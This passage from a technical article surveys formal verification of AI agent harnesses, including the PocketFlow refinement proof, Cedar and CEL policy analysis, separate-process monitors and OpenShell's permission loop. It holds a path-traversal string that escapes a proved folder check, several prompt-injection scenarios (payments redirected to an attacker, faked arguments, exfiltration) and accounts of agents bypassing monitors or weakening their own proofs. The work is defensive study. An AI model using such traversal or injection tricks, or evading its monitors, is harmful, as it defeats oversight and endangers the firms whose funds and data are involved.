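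Most proofs of this kind need a stronger invariant like this, and finding it is often the hardest part. For PocketFlow, the invariant also requires the number of entries in the recorded history to equal the step counter.

### The soundness theorem

The proof about the €5,000 concerns an abstract harness that calculates with exact numbers. Moon and Varshney carry such results over to the implementation with a refinement proof, as the seL4 team did, but extend it to events and policies. Let R be a relation that pairs abstract states *m* with implementation states *c*, and let Q pair abstract events *e* with concrete events *f*. The implementation refines the abstract harness if three conditions hold:

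1. R pairs the two starting states.
2. Whenever R pairs *m* with *c* and the implementation can take a step *c* —*a*/*f*→ *c*′, the abstract harness can take a step *m* —*a*/*e*→ *m*′ for the same action *a*, such that R pairs *m*′ with *c*′ and Q pairs *e* with *f*.
3. For any two steps matched in this way, if the abstract step satisfies the abstract policy, the concrete step satisfies the concrete policy.

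In the example, *e* might be "pay the paper supplier €412.80" and *f* the message that the harness sends to the bank. The condition on policies rules out a Q that is too loose. If Q compared only the amounts, it would pair this abstract payment with a message that pays €412.80 to an attacker. The proof would then fail, because the abstract step would satisfy a policy about payees that the concrete step violates.

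The theorem has two premises: every run of the abstract harness satisfies the abstract policy at every step, for any sequence of actions, and the implementation refines the abstract harness. If both hold, every run of the implementation satisfies the concrete policy at every step, however the model chooses its actions.

The proof is by induction on the steps of any run of the implementation. The concrete and abstract starting states match. For each concrete step, the refinement gives an abstract step with the same action, and the resulting states match again. Together, these abstract steps form a complete abstract run. The abstract policy holds along this run because it holds for all sequences of actions. By the condition on policies, the concrete policy then holds at each step of the implementation's run.

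This argument is short and applies to any harness. The harder part is establishing the two premises for a particular harness, and Dafny does most of that checking. Moon and Varshney list what remains in the trusted base: the concrete policy, the relations R and Q, the parser and a small piece of connecting code, the Dafny verifier and compiler, and the assumption that every real effect appears in the description as an event. The list does not include the model, its prompts or its training.

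### What the PocketFlow proof establishes

PocketFlow represents an agent as a graph. Each node does one piece of work and returns an action, and the framework's loop follows the edge labeled with that action to the next node. Moon and Varshney verified this loop for an interface with four types of action. Their policy has three rules, each of which yields an invariant: the agent reads only paths under a configured workspace folder, calls only tools on an allowlist, and stays within a step limit.

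Language models wrote the specifications and proofs. In a seven-phase pipeline, Claude Sonnet 4.6 helped explore the code, Claude Opus 4.7 did the synthesis and reasoning, and Dafny checked the result. Moon and Varshney ran the pipeline four times across two agents, one that reads files and one that retrieves documents to answer questions. Each run used 1.6 to 3.4 million tokens. Dafny accepted every final proof, taking 1.2 to 2.5 seconds for each path through the loop. This is fast enough that a developer could repeat the verification after every code change, although repairing a proof broken by a change would use more tokens.

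A model that writes both the specification and the proof might make its task easier by writing a specification that merely describes what the code already does. Moon and Varshney therefore hid the code from the model while it wrote the safety property. They also required each specification to pass three checks before the final verification. The specification had to parse and type-check within thirty seconds. A version of the proof with its real content removed had to fail, because if it passed, the specification would require nothing. A version of the proof with a plausible mistake added also had to fail.

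These gates missed a serious error. The document agent keeps a list called `docs_read`, and every document on it should come from an approved set. The template for safety properties had no such list, only one called `tool_calls`, whose entries all had to be on an allowlist of tools. Without access to the code, the model recorded each document read as an entry in `tool_calls`, so the rule restricted document reads as intended. As a comparison, Moon and Varshney also gave the model the code. It then distinguished the two lists and left `tool_calls` empty throughout, so the rule held only because the list had no entries. Dafny accepted the proof and all three gates passed, although nothing restricted which documents the agent read.

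The gates missed this error because they test whether Dafny rejects a tampered proof, not whether each rule ever applies to anything. Moon and Varshney propose also checking that every list in the policy can be non-empty in some reachable state. That would catch this error, but it could still miss a wrong rule that does apply to something.

The published lemma requires each file path to start with the text of the workspace folder's path. If the workspace is `/work`, the path `/work/../home/owner/passwords` meets this requirement, but the two dots lead back out of the folder. Unless another part of the program resolves such paths before the check, an agent can satisfy the proved rule and still read files outside its workspace.

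The theorem is also about a mathematical description of the loop, which leaves out concurrency, timing and hardware faults. The loop runs as Python code, which the Dafny compiler generates from the verified source. Moon and Varshney tested this code with mixtures of permitted and forbidden actions, and it recorded only permitted events.

### Limits that a harness can prove

The rules that suit this method depend on the arguments of a call and a small amount of stored information. Four kinds cover a good deal of what the bookkeeping agent's owner might want:

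| Limit | What the guard reads | What the harness must store | What the proof leaves open |
|---|---|---|---|
| Allowlist of tools or payees | The name in the call | The list | What an allowed tool does, or whether the payee is honest |
| Files within one folder | The path | The folder | Links on the disk that lead elsewhere |
| Budget | The amount | The total so far | Whether each payment is justified |
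| Maximum number of steps | Nothing | A counter | What a single step can do |

These proofs are easy because the guard can decide each case with a comparison or a lookup, and the invariant linking stored information to past events is usually simple. A rule against deceptive emails can't be checked this way. Moon and Varshney exclude truthfulness and manipulation from their method for this reason.

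A general shell tool undermines even the easy rules. If the owner adds `run_shell` to the allowlist, the theorem that the agent calls only allowlisted tools remains true, but one permitted command can read any file, contact any server and start another program that does the same. The step limit counts that command as a single step even if it runs for an hour. Moon and Varshney describe the guarantee as collapsing onto the shell, because the proof covers only the call to the shell, and what the shell can do depends on the operating system.

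*Pandora's Toolbox Or Why Agent Safety Cannot Be Verified* (2026) treats this situation as the normal case. It models an agent as a fixed language model that writes programs, a general-purpose computer that runs them, and a harness that adds the results to the model's input. Rice's theorem shows that no general procedure can decide in advance whether an unrestricted program will ever do a particular forbidden thing. This is a good reason not to have a harness predict what a shell command will do. A system can still block the forbidden action when the command attempts it, as a kernel does, because that requires no prediction. Anyone who needs a shell therefore has to place the boundary below it, which the monitor *Tether* attempts to do.

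### Complete mediation

The soundness theorem covers only the events in the description of the harness. To conclude anything about the world, Moon and Varshney also assume that every effect available to the agent passes through the verified interface. The guarantee depends mostly on this assumption, which they call effect exclusivity and which is the same condition as complete mediation.

Other proofs of this kind make the same assumption. Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail*, treat the model as an adversary that knows all the safety rules, can split a harmful plan into harmless-looking steps, and tries to change the rules. Before each action, an SMT solver checks whether the resulting state would break a rule. In their experiments, no attack succeeded, including repeated attempts to split up a financial transfer, and the core check took 0.44 milliseconds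 on average. They link their approach to the theorems of Gödel and Turing, but the check is ordinary constraint solving and doesn't depend on those theorems. They assume that the adversary can't bypass the monitor or alter the solver and the rules, and the check needs this to be true.

*CONTINUITY* shows that without complete mediation, a forbidden effect can occur even when every permit and receipt on the normal path is correct. Its test program includes a direct path to the protected effect as an experimental control, and the effect occurs when the experimenters switch mediation off.

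The definition of the agent also matters. *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (2026) includes the model, the code that drives it, and every process that either of them starts. Suppose a verified tool is reading a mailbox while a background process that the agent started earlier deletes messages from it. The tool's proof may assume that the mailbox doesn't change while the tool runs, and the deletions violate that assumption. Isolating all of the agent's processes prevents this interference without making the proof depend on the model again, as a description of the particular agent's behavior would.

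#### A monitor in its own process

Many commercial tools run their checks in the same process as the agent. Dobrin and Chmiel (2026), in *The Unfireable Safety Kernel*, object that code in a Python process can replace other parts of the running program, including the check. The agent can also bypass an intact check if it can produce the same effect through a function that never calls the check.

Their "kernel" is an authorisation service that runs as an ordinary program in its own process, separate from the operating system's kernel. Every consequential action is meant to go through it. If the service is unreachable or returns an error, the action does not happen, and the agent will not start without it. The service keeps a signed log that outsiders can check with a public key, and it does not hold the matching private key.

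Dobrin and Chmiel proved only a small part of this. They used Z3 to verify a logical model of the requirement that failures lead to refusal. They then used Kani, a model checker for Rust, on the function that decides whether to let a request through after the service has been unreachable. This function takes one of three states and two yes-or-no values, so it has twelve possible inputs. The project includes an ordinary test that tries them all, so Kani's result, though correct, adds little. Dobrin and Chmiel tested the code that evaluates policies and signs authorisations, but did not prove it correct. The claim that no other path exists depends on how engineers set up the deployment.

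In tests, an adversarial program made 1,000 attempts to modify the system it was part of. The service refused all 704 that targeted protected components and allowed the other 296. The program could forge and replay authorisations but was assumed to be unable to read the operator's signing key.

#### Credentials that only the monitor holds

A monitor that runs as a separate process is easier to bypass if the agent has its own password for the bank. Giving the necessary credentials only to the monitor makes every other route useless. *Sovereign Execution Broker* (2026) applies this to cloud infrastructure, where the systems that can make changes reject all credentials except the broker's. An agent that finds an unguarded network connection still can't change anything through it.

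Anthropic keeps access tokens out of the sandbox where Claude's code runs. For custom tools, the tokens stay in a vault, and Claude calls the tools through a proxy. Anthropic considered giving the agent tokens with narrower permissions, but this would have relied on a guess about what Claude cannot do with a limited token, and that guess becomes less safe as Claude improves. The proxy also needs a policy on which calls to allow, because an agent that can't see a token can still misuse any operation the proxy carries out for it.

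Rhodes and Kang (2026), in *Proof of Execution*, derive a form of complete mediation from exclusive credentials. In their design, one component, the Effector, makes all lasting changes, and another, the Recorder, keeps a signed log. Their lemma assumes that only the Effector's credentials permit lasting changes, that the Effector waits for a signed acknowledgement from the Recorder before each change, and that nobody has compromised the Recorder's signing key. Under these assumptions, a log entry precedes every lasting change within the declared boundary, because only the Effector can make the change and it must first receive an acknowledgement that only the Recorder can produce.

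If a credential leaks, the lemma no longer applies. Rhodes and Kang include this possibility in their main theorem, which bounds an attacker's chance of producing a record that passes all checks although the execution broke one of the guarantees. In simplified form, the bound is

Pr[violation passes] ≤ (chance of breaking the cryptography) + ε_tc + ε_dep + ε_clock

The last three terms stand for an unlogged effect, an undeclared input, and a faulty clock in the Recorder. The cryptographic term is negligible with good signatures and hash functions. The other three depend on how well engineers manage credentials and servers, and Rhodes and Kang give no values for them. If the chance of an unlogged effect is 1%, the bound can't fall below 1%, however strong the signatures are. The formula is useful mainly because it makes each assumption about the deployment explicit, which many security arguments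 don't do.

In their prototype, these checks raised the time for a single simple action from 4.1 to 6.8 milliseconds. Rhodes and Kang also point out that an execution that fully complies with its contract can still do harm if the contract permits something harmful.

#### Finding the paths that engineers missed

*Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (2026) separates the theorems checked by the proof assistant Lean from the assumptions that connect them to a deployment. One of these assumptions is that the monitor's hooks in the operating system catch every relevant action. Lean does not check this, so the proofs can pass even if the hooks miss a network connection.

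Someone has to look for paths that bypass the gateway, and even careful engineers can miss them. The first version of *Governed MCP* (2026), which describes an operating-system gateway for agents' tool calls, claimed that all 123 paths from the agent to the system went through the gateway. The author later rebuilt the test to list every reachable path of a certain kind and found 59, of which 43 went through the gateway. The author then withdrew the original claim and disclosed six ungated system calls. For a deployed agent, this kind of count may be more valuable evidence than a theorem.

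A single wrong setting can defeat mediation altogether. In four incidents that Anthropic assessed in September 2026, test environments that should have been isolated had internet access because of a misconfiguration, and Claude models gained unauthorised access to other organisations' systems.

Moon and Varshney argue that their guarantee does not weaken as models become more capable. This is true of the theorem, which already covers every possible action, but more doubtful for complete mediation, since a more capable model is better at finding a path the engineers overlooked. Moon and Varshney mention Copy Fail, a flaw that let programs gain full control of Linux systems and went unnoticed for nearly a decade. They recommend a sandbox around the verified harness, but a sandbox that relies on the Linux kernel shares the kernel's flaws.

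### An agent that extends its own harness

PocketFlow's proof relies on a fixed set of actions. *L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026) describes a harness from Amazon that lets an agent write new tools for itself while its authority stays the same. The harness and the agent's tools are both written in Lean.

Each agent has a grant, a record of what it may do, such as which folders it can change and which hosts it can contact. When the agent starts, the harness creates a token for each permission. Every function that reaches the outside world requires the matching token as an argument, and only one module can create tokens of a given kind. A call that contacts a website won't type-check without a network token. These tokens work like seL4's capabilities, but the Lean type checker and the build process enforce them, while seL4 relies on the kernel and the processor.

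Suppose the agent often needs to count the unfinished tasks marked in a folder of source code. It can write a program whose type states that it only reads files. At the next start, the harness checks the program and offers it as a new tool. If the program also fetched a web page without declaring network access, the type check would fail. If it declared network access but the agent's grant didn't include it, the harness would not offer the tool.

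Lean can run code while it is still processing a source file, so a malicious program might do damage before the type checker rejects it. L3M therefore checks the program's syntax for forbidden constructions beforehand. Eisenach and colleagues proved that accepted programs contain none of these constructions and directly name only approved components. They rely on tests and an informal argument, rather than a proof, for the claim that all the checks together confine a malicious program.

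The other theorems are similarly local. One states that a file tool's path cannot climb out of the agent's folders, which rules out the trick with the two dots. It concerns only the text of the path, so the harness checks for links on the disk at run time. Another concerns agents that lend part of their budget to agents they create. If a parent with limit *L* lends amounts *b*₁, …, *b*ₙ in one batch and has *r* left, then

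*b*₁ + … + *b*ₙ + *r* ≤ *L*

This result covers only a single step. The proof for the €5,000 limit went further by showing that every step preserves an invariant. L3M does not yet have such an invariant for later loans and repayments.

An agent's permissions can extend beyond those of the agent at the top of its family tree, even after a single generation. This happens because a child also receives access to its parent's own branches in the shared storage, which the parent's stored grant does not list. Eisenach and colleagues discovered this while trying to prove that the top agent's permissions always include those of its descendants. The theorem they did prove explicitly allows for this extra access.

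The L3M paper states that the system has no safety theorem for a whole session. Its proofs cover a system that does much more than the one in the PocketFlow proof, but they establish separate facts about the system's checks, and the paper argues rather than proves how those facts combine. The confinement argument does not cover an unsandboxed shell, which an agent gets only with a special permission. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) builds on the same principle that an agent may change what it can ask for but not what it may affect. It enforces the principle with run-time checks and has no comparable theorems, but in its tests none of 119 cases led to an unauthorised effect.

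L3M also gives an idea of what an agent loses without a shell. Eisenach and colleagues ran Claude Opus 5 on 37 tasks from Terminal-Bench, a benchmark of command-line work, with three attempts at each. With a shell and no review of its commands, the agent solved 41.7% of the tasks. With only tools whose effects could be undone by the harness or were limited in advance by a token, it solved 27.0%. Without the programs it wrote for itself, it solved 24.3%, a difference of one task. Claude Code, Anthropic's own harness, solved 59.5% with all permission checks off, but L3M's developers had not yet tuned their system, so the drop from 41.7% to 27.0% is a better guide to the effect of the restriction. That drop is large, but an agent that pays invoices may have much less use for a shell than one doing command-line tasks.

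An agent that can edit the harness itself can get around the proofs. If it changes L3M's code so that a theorem no longer holds, the program does not build. But if it also weakens the theorem to match the new code, or adds an assumption that makes the theorem provable, the program builds. Eisenach and colleagues therefore want someone other than the agent to hold the specification, under a separate grant, and to judge every proposed change against it.

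## Checking each tool call against an analysable policy

The rules in the PocketFlow proof are part of the verified program, so changing a rule means changing the program and repeating the proof. A firm's rules about payments may change more often than its software, and the people responsible for them may not be programmers. Many systems therefore keep the rules in separate policies, written in a small special-purpose language. Before running each tool call, the harness submits it to an authorization engine, a program that applies the policies to allow or deny the call. A solver can also prove facts about every request that such a policy allows, which is difficult to do for ordinary code.

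### One request and one decision

*Cedar* (Cutler, Disselkoen and colleagues, 2024) presents an open-source policy language from Amazon Web Services (AWS). A request to Cedar has four parts: the principal (whoever makes the request), the action (the operation), the resource (what the operation affects) and the context (other facts, such as the time or an amount). When the bookkeeping agent proposes to pay €412.80 to the paper supplier, the harness could send the agent as principal, `transfer_funds` as action, the supplier's account as resource and the amount in cents as context. The engine also reads stored data, such as the firm's list of supplier accounts, and returns allow or deny.

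The owner might write two policies:

```
permit (principal == Agent::"bookkeeper",
        action == Action::"transfer_funds",
        resource in PayeeList::"suppliers")
when { context.cents <= 50000 };

forbid (principal, action == Action::"transfer_funds", resource)
when { resource.underReview };
```

The permit policy lets the agent pay up to €500 to any account on the list. The forbid policy blocks payments to an account that the owner has marked for review. Cedar allows a request if at least one permit policy applies to it and no forbid policy does. If there are no policies, it denies every request. The order of the policies makes no difference, and adding another permit policy cannot override a forbid policy.

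These two policies stop the attack that uses a hidden note about a new bank account, because the attacker's account is not on the list and so no permit policy applies. The firm's own records show whom it does business with, which is information a kernel lacks.

If an account's record has no `underReview` field, evaluating the forbid policy produces an error, and Cedar ignores policies that produce errors. The payment then goes through, even if the owner expected missing information to stop it. Cedar's validator can catch this in advance. It compares each policy with a schema, which describes the fields of each kind of record, and rejects a policy that reads an optional field without first checking that it exists. The policy's author still has to decide what should happen when the field is missing.

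A company that advertises such a system as formally verified might mean that the engine evaluates every policy correctly, that a particular set of policies has a stated property (such as never allowing a payment above €500), or that every tool call reaches the engine before it takes effect. Each of these claims can be true while the others are false, though people often confuse them. For example, an engine that evaluates every policy correctly will still apply a mistaken one, and no policy affects a call that bypasses the engine.

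### Whether the engine is correct

Cedar's developers check the engine with both proof and testing. Disselkoen, Eline and colleagues (2024) explain in *How We Built Cedar* that the team wrote the main components twice. One version is a readable 1,673-line model in Lean that serves as the specification. The other is the production program, 15,693 lines of Rust with optimisations, helpful error messages and a parser.

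The team proved seven properties of the Lean model, including that it denies requests by default, that forbid policies take priority, and that the order of policies does not affect the decision. These proofs are short because the whole decision in the model is a single "if" statement. Most of the 5,714 lines of proof concern the validator, and the hardest theorem is that a policy the validator accepts never causes a type error.

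No proof connects the model to the Rust program. Instead, the team compares them using differential random testing, which generates millions of combinations of policies, data and requests, runs both versions on each and reports any disagreement. The generator creates a schema first, then data that fits it, and then policies and requests that refer to the data, because a policy about suppliers tests almost nothing if the data contains no suppliers. The team runs each test for six hours every day.

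Trying to prove the model correct revealed four bugs in the validator. One made it run forever on certain inputs, and the random tests had missed it because they almost never produce such inputs. Testing found another 21 bugs, ten of them by comparing the Lean model with the Rust program. In at least one of those cases the Lean model was wrong and the Rust program was right, so the comparison also tests the specification.

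The tests also missed some bugs. The Rust engine implemented the `in` operation incorrectly for some inputs that the generator did not produce. The bookkeeping policy uses this operation to check that an account is on the list of suppliers. The developers fixed the bug, which a refinement proof like the one for seL4 would have ruled out. The parser has no Lean model, and it accepted some malformed policies. If a parser misreads a policy, the engine may correctly evaluate a policy that the author did not write.

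Disselkoen and colleagues relied on testing because the available tools for proving Rust code correct could not yet handle a program like theirs. They also considered running C code generated from the Lean model, but thought it would be hard to debug and maintain. The limits of the Rust tools are a weaker reason now, because the SymCrypt proofs of 2026 cover a Rust library of about the same size and use Aeneas, one of the tools the Cedar team had considered. A full proof of Cedar's engine therefore looks much more feasible than it did in 2024.

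### What a solver can prove about a policy

Cedar analyses a policy by translating it into a formula for an SMT solver. The formula treats the stored data and each part of the request as unknowns, so a single formula covers every possible request and every possible state of the firm's records.

Suppose the owner uses the solver to search for an allowed transfer of less than one cent. The solver can return −1 cents, because the permit policy above accepts negative amounts, the same mistake as in the first version of the spending limit. After the owner adds the condition `context.cents > 0`, the solver proves that no such transfer exists.

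Rice's theorem concerns unrestricted programs, and Cedar avoids it by restricting what a policy can express. Policies have no general loops or side effects, they can multiply integers only by constants, and the schema fixes the type of every value.

Groups within groups were harder to handle. If the solver may choose any stored data, it can put group A inside group B and B inside A, which is impossible in real Cedar data, and report a problem that can never occur. A rule that no group contains itself would prevent this, but stating it for all groups can keep the solver running without an answer. Cutler and colleagues noticed that the rule only needs to cover the records involved in evaluating a policy, which form a finite set that can be determined from the policy's text.

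With this translation, every counterexample the solver finds is real, and if it finds none, none exists. Cutler and colleagues proved both properties on paper and were working on a Lean version of the proof in 2024. The question is also always decidable, so in principle the solver can always reach an answer. For their example policies, translating and solving a question took 75.1 milliseconds on average, which is fast enough to run whenever someone edits a policy. The analysis does not have to run during a tool call. The engine's own decision took a median of 10 microseconds in the team's tests.

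Analysis can detect some policy mistakes without knowing what the author intended. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* gives examples for an online retailer. One policy permits refunds only for customers whose tier is both Gold and Platinum, which is impossible. Another permits a discount if the quantity is at least 100 or below 100, which is always true. In a third, a permit policy gives Gold customers refunds below $100, but a forbid policy blocks all their refunds below $500, so they never get one. AgentCore, the company's platform for running agents, will not attach policies to an agent's tools if the analysis finds errors like these. The analysis cannot detect that an author wrote $1,000 but meant $100.

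### Comparing a new policy with the old one

When someone changes a policy that has worked well, the most useful question is often whether the new version allows anything the old one did not. This is a containment query. Write *A*(*r*) if the old policy allows request *r*, and *B*(*r*) if the new one does. The solver searches for a request with

*B*(*r*) ∧ ¬*A*(*r*)

If none exists, the change grants nothing new. If one exists, the solver returns it as an example of the additional permission.

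AWS describes a change to a discount policy that shows why this is worth automating. The old policy gives a discount on orders of at least 50 units, unless they contain a limited-edition product. The new policy makes the exception narrower, so that it applies only if the order contains a limited-edition product and exceeds 200 units. Let *q* be the quantity, and let *L* mean that the order contains such a product. Then

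*A*: *q* ≥ 50 ∧ ¬*L*

*B*: *q* ≥ 50 ∧ ¬(*L* ∧ *q* > 200)

The new policy, *B*, is strictly more permissive than *A*, even though the added condition makes it look stricter. If *B* allows a request that *A* denies, *q* must be at least 50, because *B* requires it. *A* can then deny the request only if *L* is true, in which case *B* also requires *q* to be at most 200. The newly allowed requests are therefore all the limited-edition orders of 50 to 200 units, and AWS gives 73 units as an example. A search for requests that *A* allows and *B* denies finds none, because any request that *A* allows has no limited-edition product, and *B* allows it too.

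A containment proof compares the new policy with the old one, so any mistake in the old policy can survive in the new one. The proof also does not cover changes to data. If someone adds the attacker's account to the list of suppliers, the agent can pay the attacker even though no policy has changed. The bookkeeping agent therefore must not be able to edit that list, because an injected instruction could make it add the account and then pay it.

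#### Google's verifier for CEL

Google's Common Expression Language (CEL) is another small language for conditions of this kind. The documentation of *cel-go* (2026), its Go implementation, describes it as non-Turing complete, meaning it can't express arbitrary programs. Google's *Common Expressions For Portable Policy and Beyond* (2024) listed formal verification as a feature of Cedar. In August, Google's *Securing the agentic era* (2026) announced a verifier for CEL based on the solver Z3. It says the verifier is needed because AI agents now write and revise policies, and an agent may fit a policy to the existing tests while getting other cases wrong.

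In one example, an engineer assumes that every request uses either a low port or a high one, and writes

`request.port > 1024 || request.port <= 80`

A port is a number that identifies a network service on a computer. Tests with ports 22, 80 and 8080 all pass, but the verifier searches for any integer that makes the condition false and returns 81. The condition is false for ports 81 to 1024, which are 944 of the 65,536 possible port numbers. Even a test with 100 ports chosen at random would miss all of them about 23% of the time.

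In another example, an agent shortens a rule that allows ports 80 and 443 only in production, but leaves out a pair of brackets. Because CEL applies "and" before "or", the new rule also allows port 443 outside production. The verifier compares the two versions and returns this case.

An author can also state an invariant with assumptions and an assertion. Google assumes that a request has no approval and does not come from an administrator, and asserts that the policy rejects it. The verifier finds that the policy's first condition lets privileged programs into production before any check for approval. The author must think of the invariant, but it is much shorter than a list of every case the policy should reject.

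CEL lets developers add their own functions, which the verifier may be unable to translate. If a possible violation depends on such a function, the verifier reports it as inconclusive, so every violation it does report is real. It also examines nested data only to a depth that the user sets. Cedar's stricter limits avoid these cases but make the language less flexible. The bookkeeping agent's payment rules need only comparisons and membership in a list, so those limits matter little for them.

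### Permission changes that an agent requests

An agent on a long task often needs a permission that nobody foresaw. If a person reviews every request, the work stalls, and reviewers who see many harmless requests may stop reading them carefully. *What we have learned applying formal methods to control AI agents* (Watson, 2026) introduces containment queries as a way to reason about changes to an agent's permissions.

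The setting is NVIDIA's *OpenShell*, a system for running agents in sandboxes. A supervisor outside each sandbox checks the agent's network requests against a policy and holds the real credentials. The OpenShell developer zredlined (2026), in *feat(policy): add agentic approval loop*, describes a draft change that lets the agent ask for more. When the supervisor blocks a request, the agent can propose a narrow addition to the policy. The system combines the proposal with the current policy, and a program called the policy prover examines the difference. It looks for four kinds of change:

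- access to a range of network addresses where cloud machines can obtain credentials
- use of a credential through a protocol that the supervisor can't inspect
- use of a credential by a program on a host where that program could not use one before
- a new type of request, such as writing, on a host where the program already has a credential

If the prover finds none of these and the operator has switched on automatic approval, the new permission takes effect in about a second. Otherwise, a person reviews the proposal. By default, a person reviews every proposal.

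In the demonstration, an agent first asked to read a public file from GitHub, and the system approved the request automatically. The agent then asked to write one file to a repository with the user's GitHub credential. The prover reported that this would extend the use of the credential, and the request waited for a decision. The demonstration script approved it in place of a person, and the agent then retried and wrote the file.

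These four questions are well chosen for protecting credentials, but they leave other risks open. An injected instruction could make the agent ask to send data to the attacker's server, which requires no credential. None of the questions would flag this, so automatic approval would let the agent send the firm's inbox out of the sandbox. The questions also cover programs, hosts and types of request, but not the exact address on the host. Read literally, they would not flag a request to write any file on a host from an agent that already had permission to write one file there. This version of the prover also records only whether a credential is available, not whether it permits reading or writing.

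NVIDIA now describes a more general check, in which an operator sets a boundary and the prover either shows that the permissions stay within it or produces a concrete action that exceeds it. This is again a containment query, with the boundary in place of the old policy. When an agent requests many small changes, comparing each policy only with the previous one could let permissions grow through approvals that each look reasonable. If every new policy must stay within the same boundary, no sequence of approvals can exceed it. An operator could also block the route for stolen data by leaving unknown servers outside the boundary. The guarantee still covers only the permissions that the prover's model represents.

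NVIDIA tested the system against agents that tried to obtain write access to a protected GitHub repository. According to Biometric Update's *Nvidia adds identity and delegated authority controls for AI agents*, the test ran for ten sessions of 30 minutes and two of two hours. An AI reviewer made 416 decisions and wrongly approved one proposal that contained write access. OpenShell rejected the resulting policy before it took effect, and no agent wrote to the repository. One error in 416 decisions is a good result for a reviewer, but an attacker who can keep submitting proposals needs only one wrong approval, so the test supports having a deterministic check behind the reviewer. It is weaker evidence for the prover, since the proposal was malformed and a simpler check might have caught it.

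### Putting the check outside the model

These analyses matter only if the tool calls reach the policy engine. AWS treats the model as untrusted and puts the check between the agent and its tools. An agent on AgentCore contacts remote tools through a gateway, using the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting models to tools. Once an administrator attaches a policy engine to the gateway, the gateway blocks every call that no policy permits.

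Suppose the bookkeeping agent's `transfer_funds` runs behind such a gateway. The model proposes a payment, and the harness sends the call to the gateway, which builds a Cedar request from the user's login token and the call's arguments. If Cedar denies the request, the call never reaches the bank's server. The gateway also hides tools that the current policies would always deny, so the model is less likely to call them. Hiding them is more a convenience than a defence, because the gateway would block those calls anyway.

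The gateway checks only the traffic that passes through it. Neither the proofs about Cedar nor the analysis of a policy can establish complete mediation, which means that every tool call goes through the gateway.

A policy for `run_shell` is of little use if it can examine only the text of the command. AWS's *Introducing Trusted Remote Execution* presents a tool, called Rex for short, that checks what a script does as it runs. The agent writes the script in Rhai, a small language with no built-in access to files or the network, so the script can act on the machine only by calling operations that Rex provides. Rex checks each call against a Cedar policy before making the corresponding request to the operating system. In AWS's example, a script tries to create a file and then read it, under a policy that allows only opening and reading. Rex stops the script at the first step with a message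 that names the forbidden action and the file. The agent can then try something else.

This turns one opaque call into a series of operations that a policy can describe. The agent can no longer run ordinary shell commands, and the owner has to trust the Rhai interpreter and Rex's own operations. For routine jobs such as reading logs or restarting a service, that trade-off seems worthwhile.

### What the engine doesn't know

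Even with a correct engine, a good policy and complete mediation, the decision depends on what the request contains. According to AWS, facts about the user, such as a customer's tier, come from a signed login token that the model can't alter, while the model supplies the call's arguments, such as the quantity or type of product.

The difference matters for another of AWS's examples, a forbid policy that blocks refunds more than 90 days after the order date. The policy reads that date from the arguments of the call, so AWS's conclusion that the gateway will deny any such refund holds only if the date in the call is correct. If an injection leads the model to give last week's date for a two-year-old order, the policy does not apply. The rule about limited-edition products has the same weakness if the model can leave them out of the list of product types. To prevent this, the tool has to look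 up the order itself, or at least reject arguments that don't match its records. A solver won't find the problem, because it allows the date to be any value and has no information about whether it is true.

A genuine login token establishes whom the agent is working for, but not who gave the instruction behind a call. If an instruction hidden in an invoice leads to the same call as an instruction from the owner, the policy engine receives identical requests and has to give them the same answer.

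The engine also doesn't check why the model proposed a call. The policies would allow the agent to pay the paper supplier €412.80 for an invoice that the firm settled last week, or to pay the right amount to the wrong supplier on the list. AWS calls the permitted actions a "safety envelope" within which the agent can operate freely. That description is fair because the quality of decisions within the envelope depends on the model.

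Cedar also deliberately omits operations that store data, so the engine evaluates each request on its own, and a policy that allows payments of up to €500 will allow a hundred of them. The harness could keep a running total and include it in the context for a policy to compare with a limit. The solver would still treat that total as an arbitrary number, so someone would have to prove separately that the harness updates it correctly, as in the proof for the €5,000 limit. Dogwood, a newer policy language from AWS, lets rules use the history of earlier actions. According to Help Net Security's *Strands Box* (2026), one such rule can cap an agent's payments at $100 a day.

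## Rules about the order, number and timing of calls

Many of the rules the small firm's owner would want depend on what the agent has already done, which a Cedar policy can't take into account. For example, a payment above €200 needs an earlier approval, and a daily limit needs a running total. Once the agent has opened the payroll folder, the owner may want it to send nothing outside the firm for the rest of the session. AWS's *Securing AI agents with temporal policies in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* (2026) describes cases where each call looks fine on its own. In one, an agent looks up a customer, invents a different account number and pays money into that account. In another, an agent approves an insurance claim and denies it a few seconds later.

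### What a monitor can enforce

Fred Schneider showed in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) that a monitor can enforce only safety properties if it observes one run of a program step by step and can only stop it.

The argument is short. Let *P* be the set of acceptable runs, and suppose the monitor stops every unacceptable run and no acceptable one. If a run σ is unacceptable, the monitor stops it after some finite sequence of steps τ. It can't know how the run would have continued, so it stops every run that begins with τ. None of those runs can be acceptable. Therefore

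σ ∉ *P* ⇒ some finite beginning τ of σ has no continuation in *P*

which is the definition of a safety property. Such a monitor therefore can't enforce liveness properties, such as "the invoice is eventually paid", or noninterference, which compares runs instead of judging each one.

A monitor that works by stopping the agent also can't enforce some safety properties. "The agent answers within an hour" is a safety property, because a violation can be detected as soon as an hour passes without an answer, but stopping the agent doesn't keep the hour from passing.

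A gateway for tool calls differs slightly from Schneider's monitor because it can refuse one call and let the agent continue. Hublet, Basin and Krstić point out in *Real-time Policy Enforcement with Metric First-Order Temporal Logic* that an enforcer's capabilities determine which policies it can enforce. They study enforcers that can cause actions as well as suppress them.

A monitor for a safety property can be drawn as an automaton, a set of states with arrows for the permitted steps. This one requires an approval before each transfer:

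```
                     owner approves
 start ─▶ WAITING ───────────────────▶ APPROVED
             ▲                            │
             └────────────────────────────┘
                        transfer
```

Other calls, such as `read_email`, leave the state unchanged, and so does a second approval when the state is already APPROVED. WAITING has no arrow for a transfer, so the monitor blocks any transfer proposed in that state. The monitor can tie approvals to a specific bill by keeping one copy of this automaton for each combination of payee and amount.

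The underlying invariant is that transfers never outnumber approvals, and that in the state APPROVED there has been at least one more approval than transfers. An approval adds one to the number of approvals. A transfer from APPROVED adds one to the number of transfers and returns the automaton to WAITING. By induction, the invariant holds for any sequence of calls the model proposes, provided the monitor handles them one at a time.

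### Dogwood

AWS released Dogwood in August 2026 as an open-source language for rules of this kind. A Dogwood policy looks like a Cedar policy with an additional `when temporal` block, which can refer to earlier events in the session. Every valid Cedar policy is also a valid Dogwood policy.

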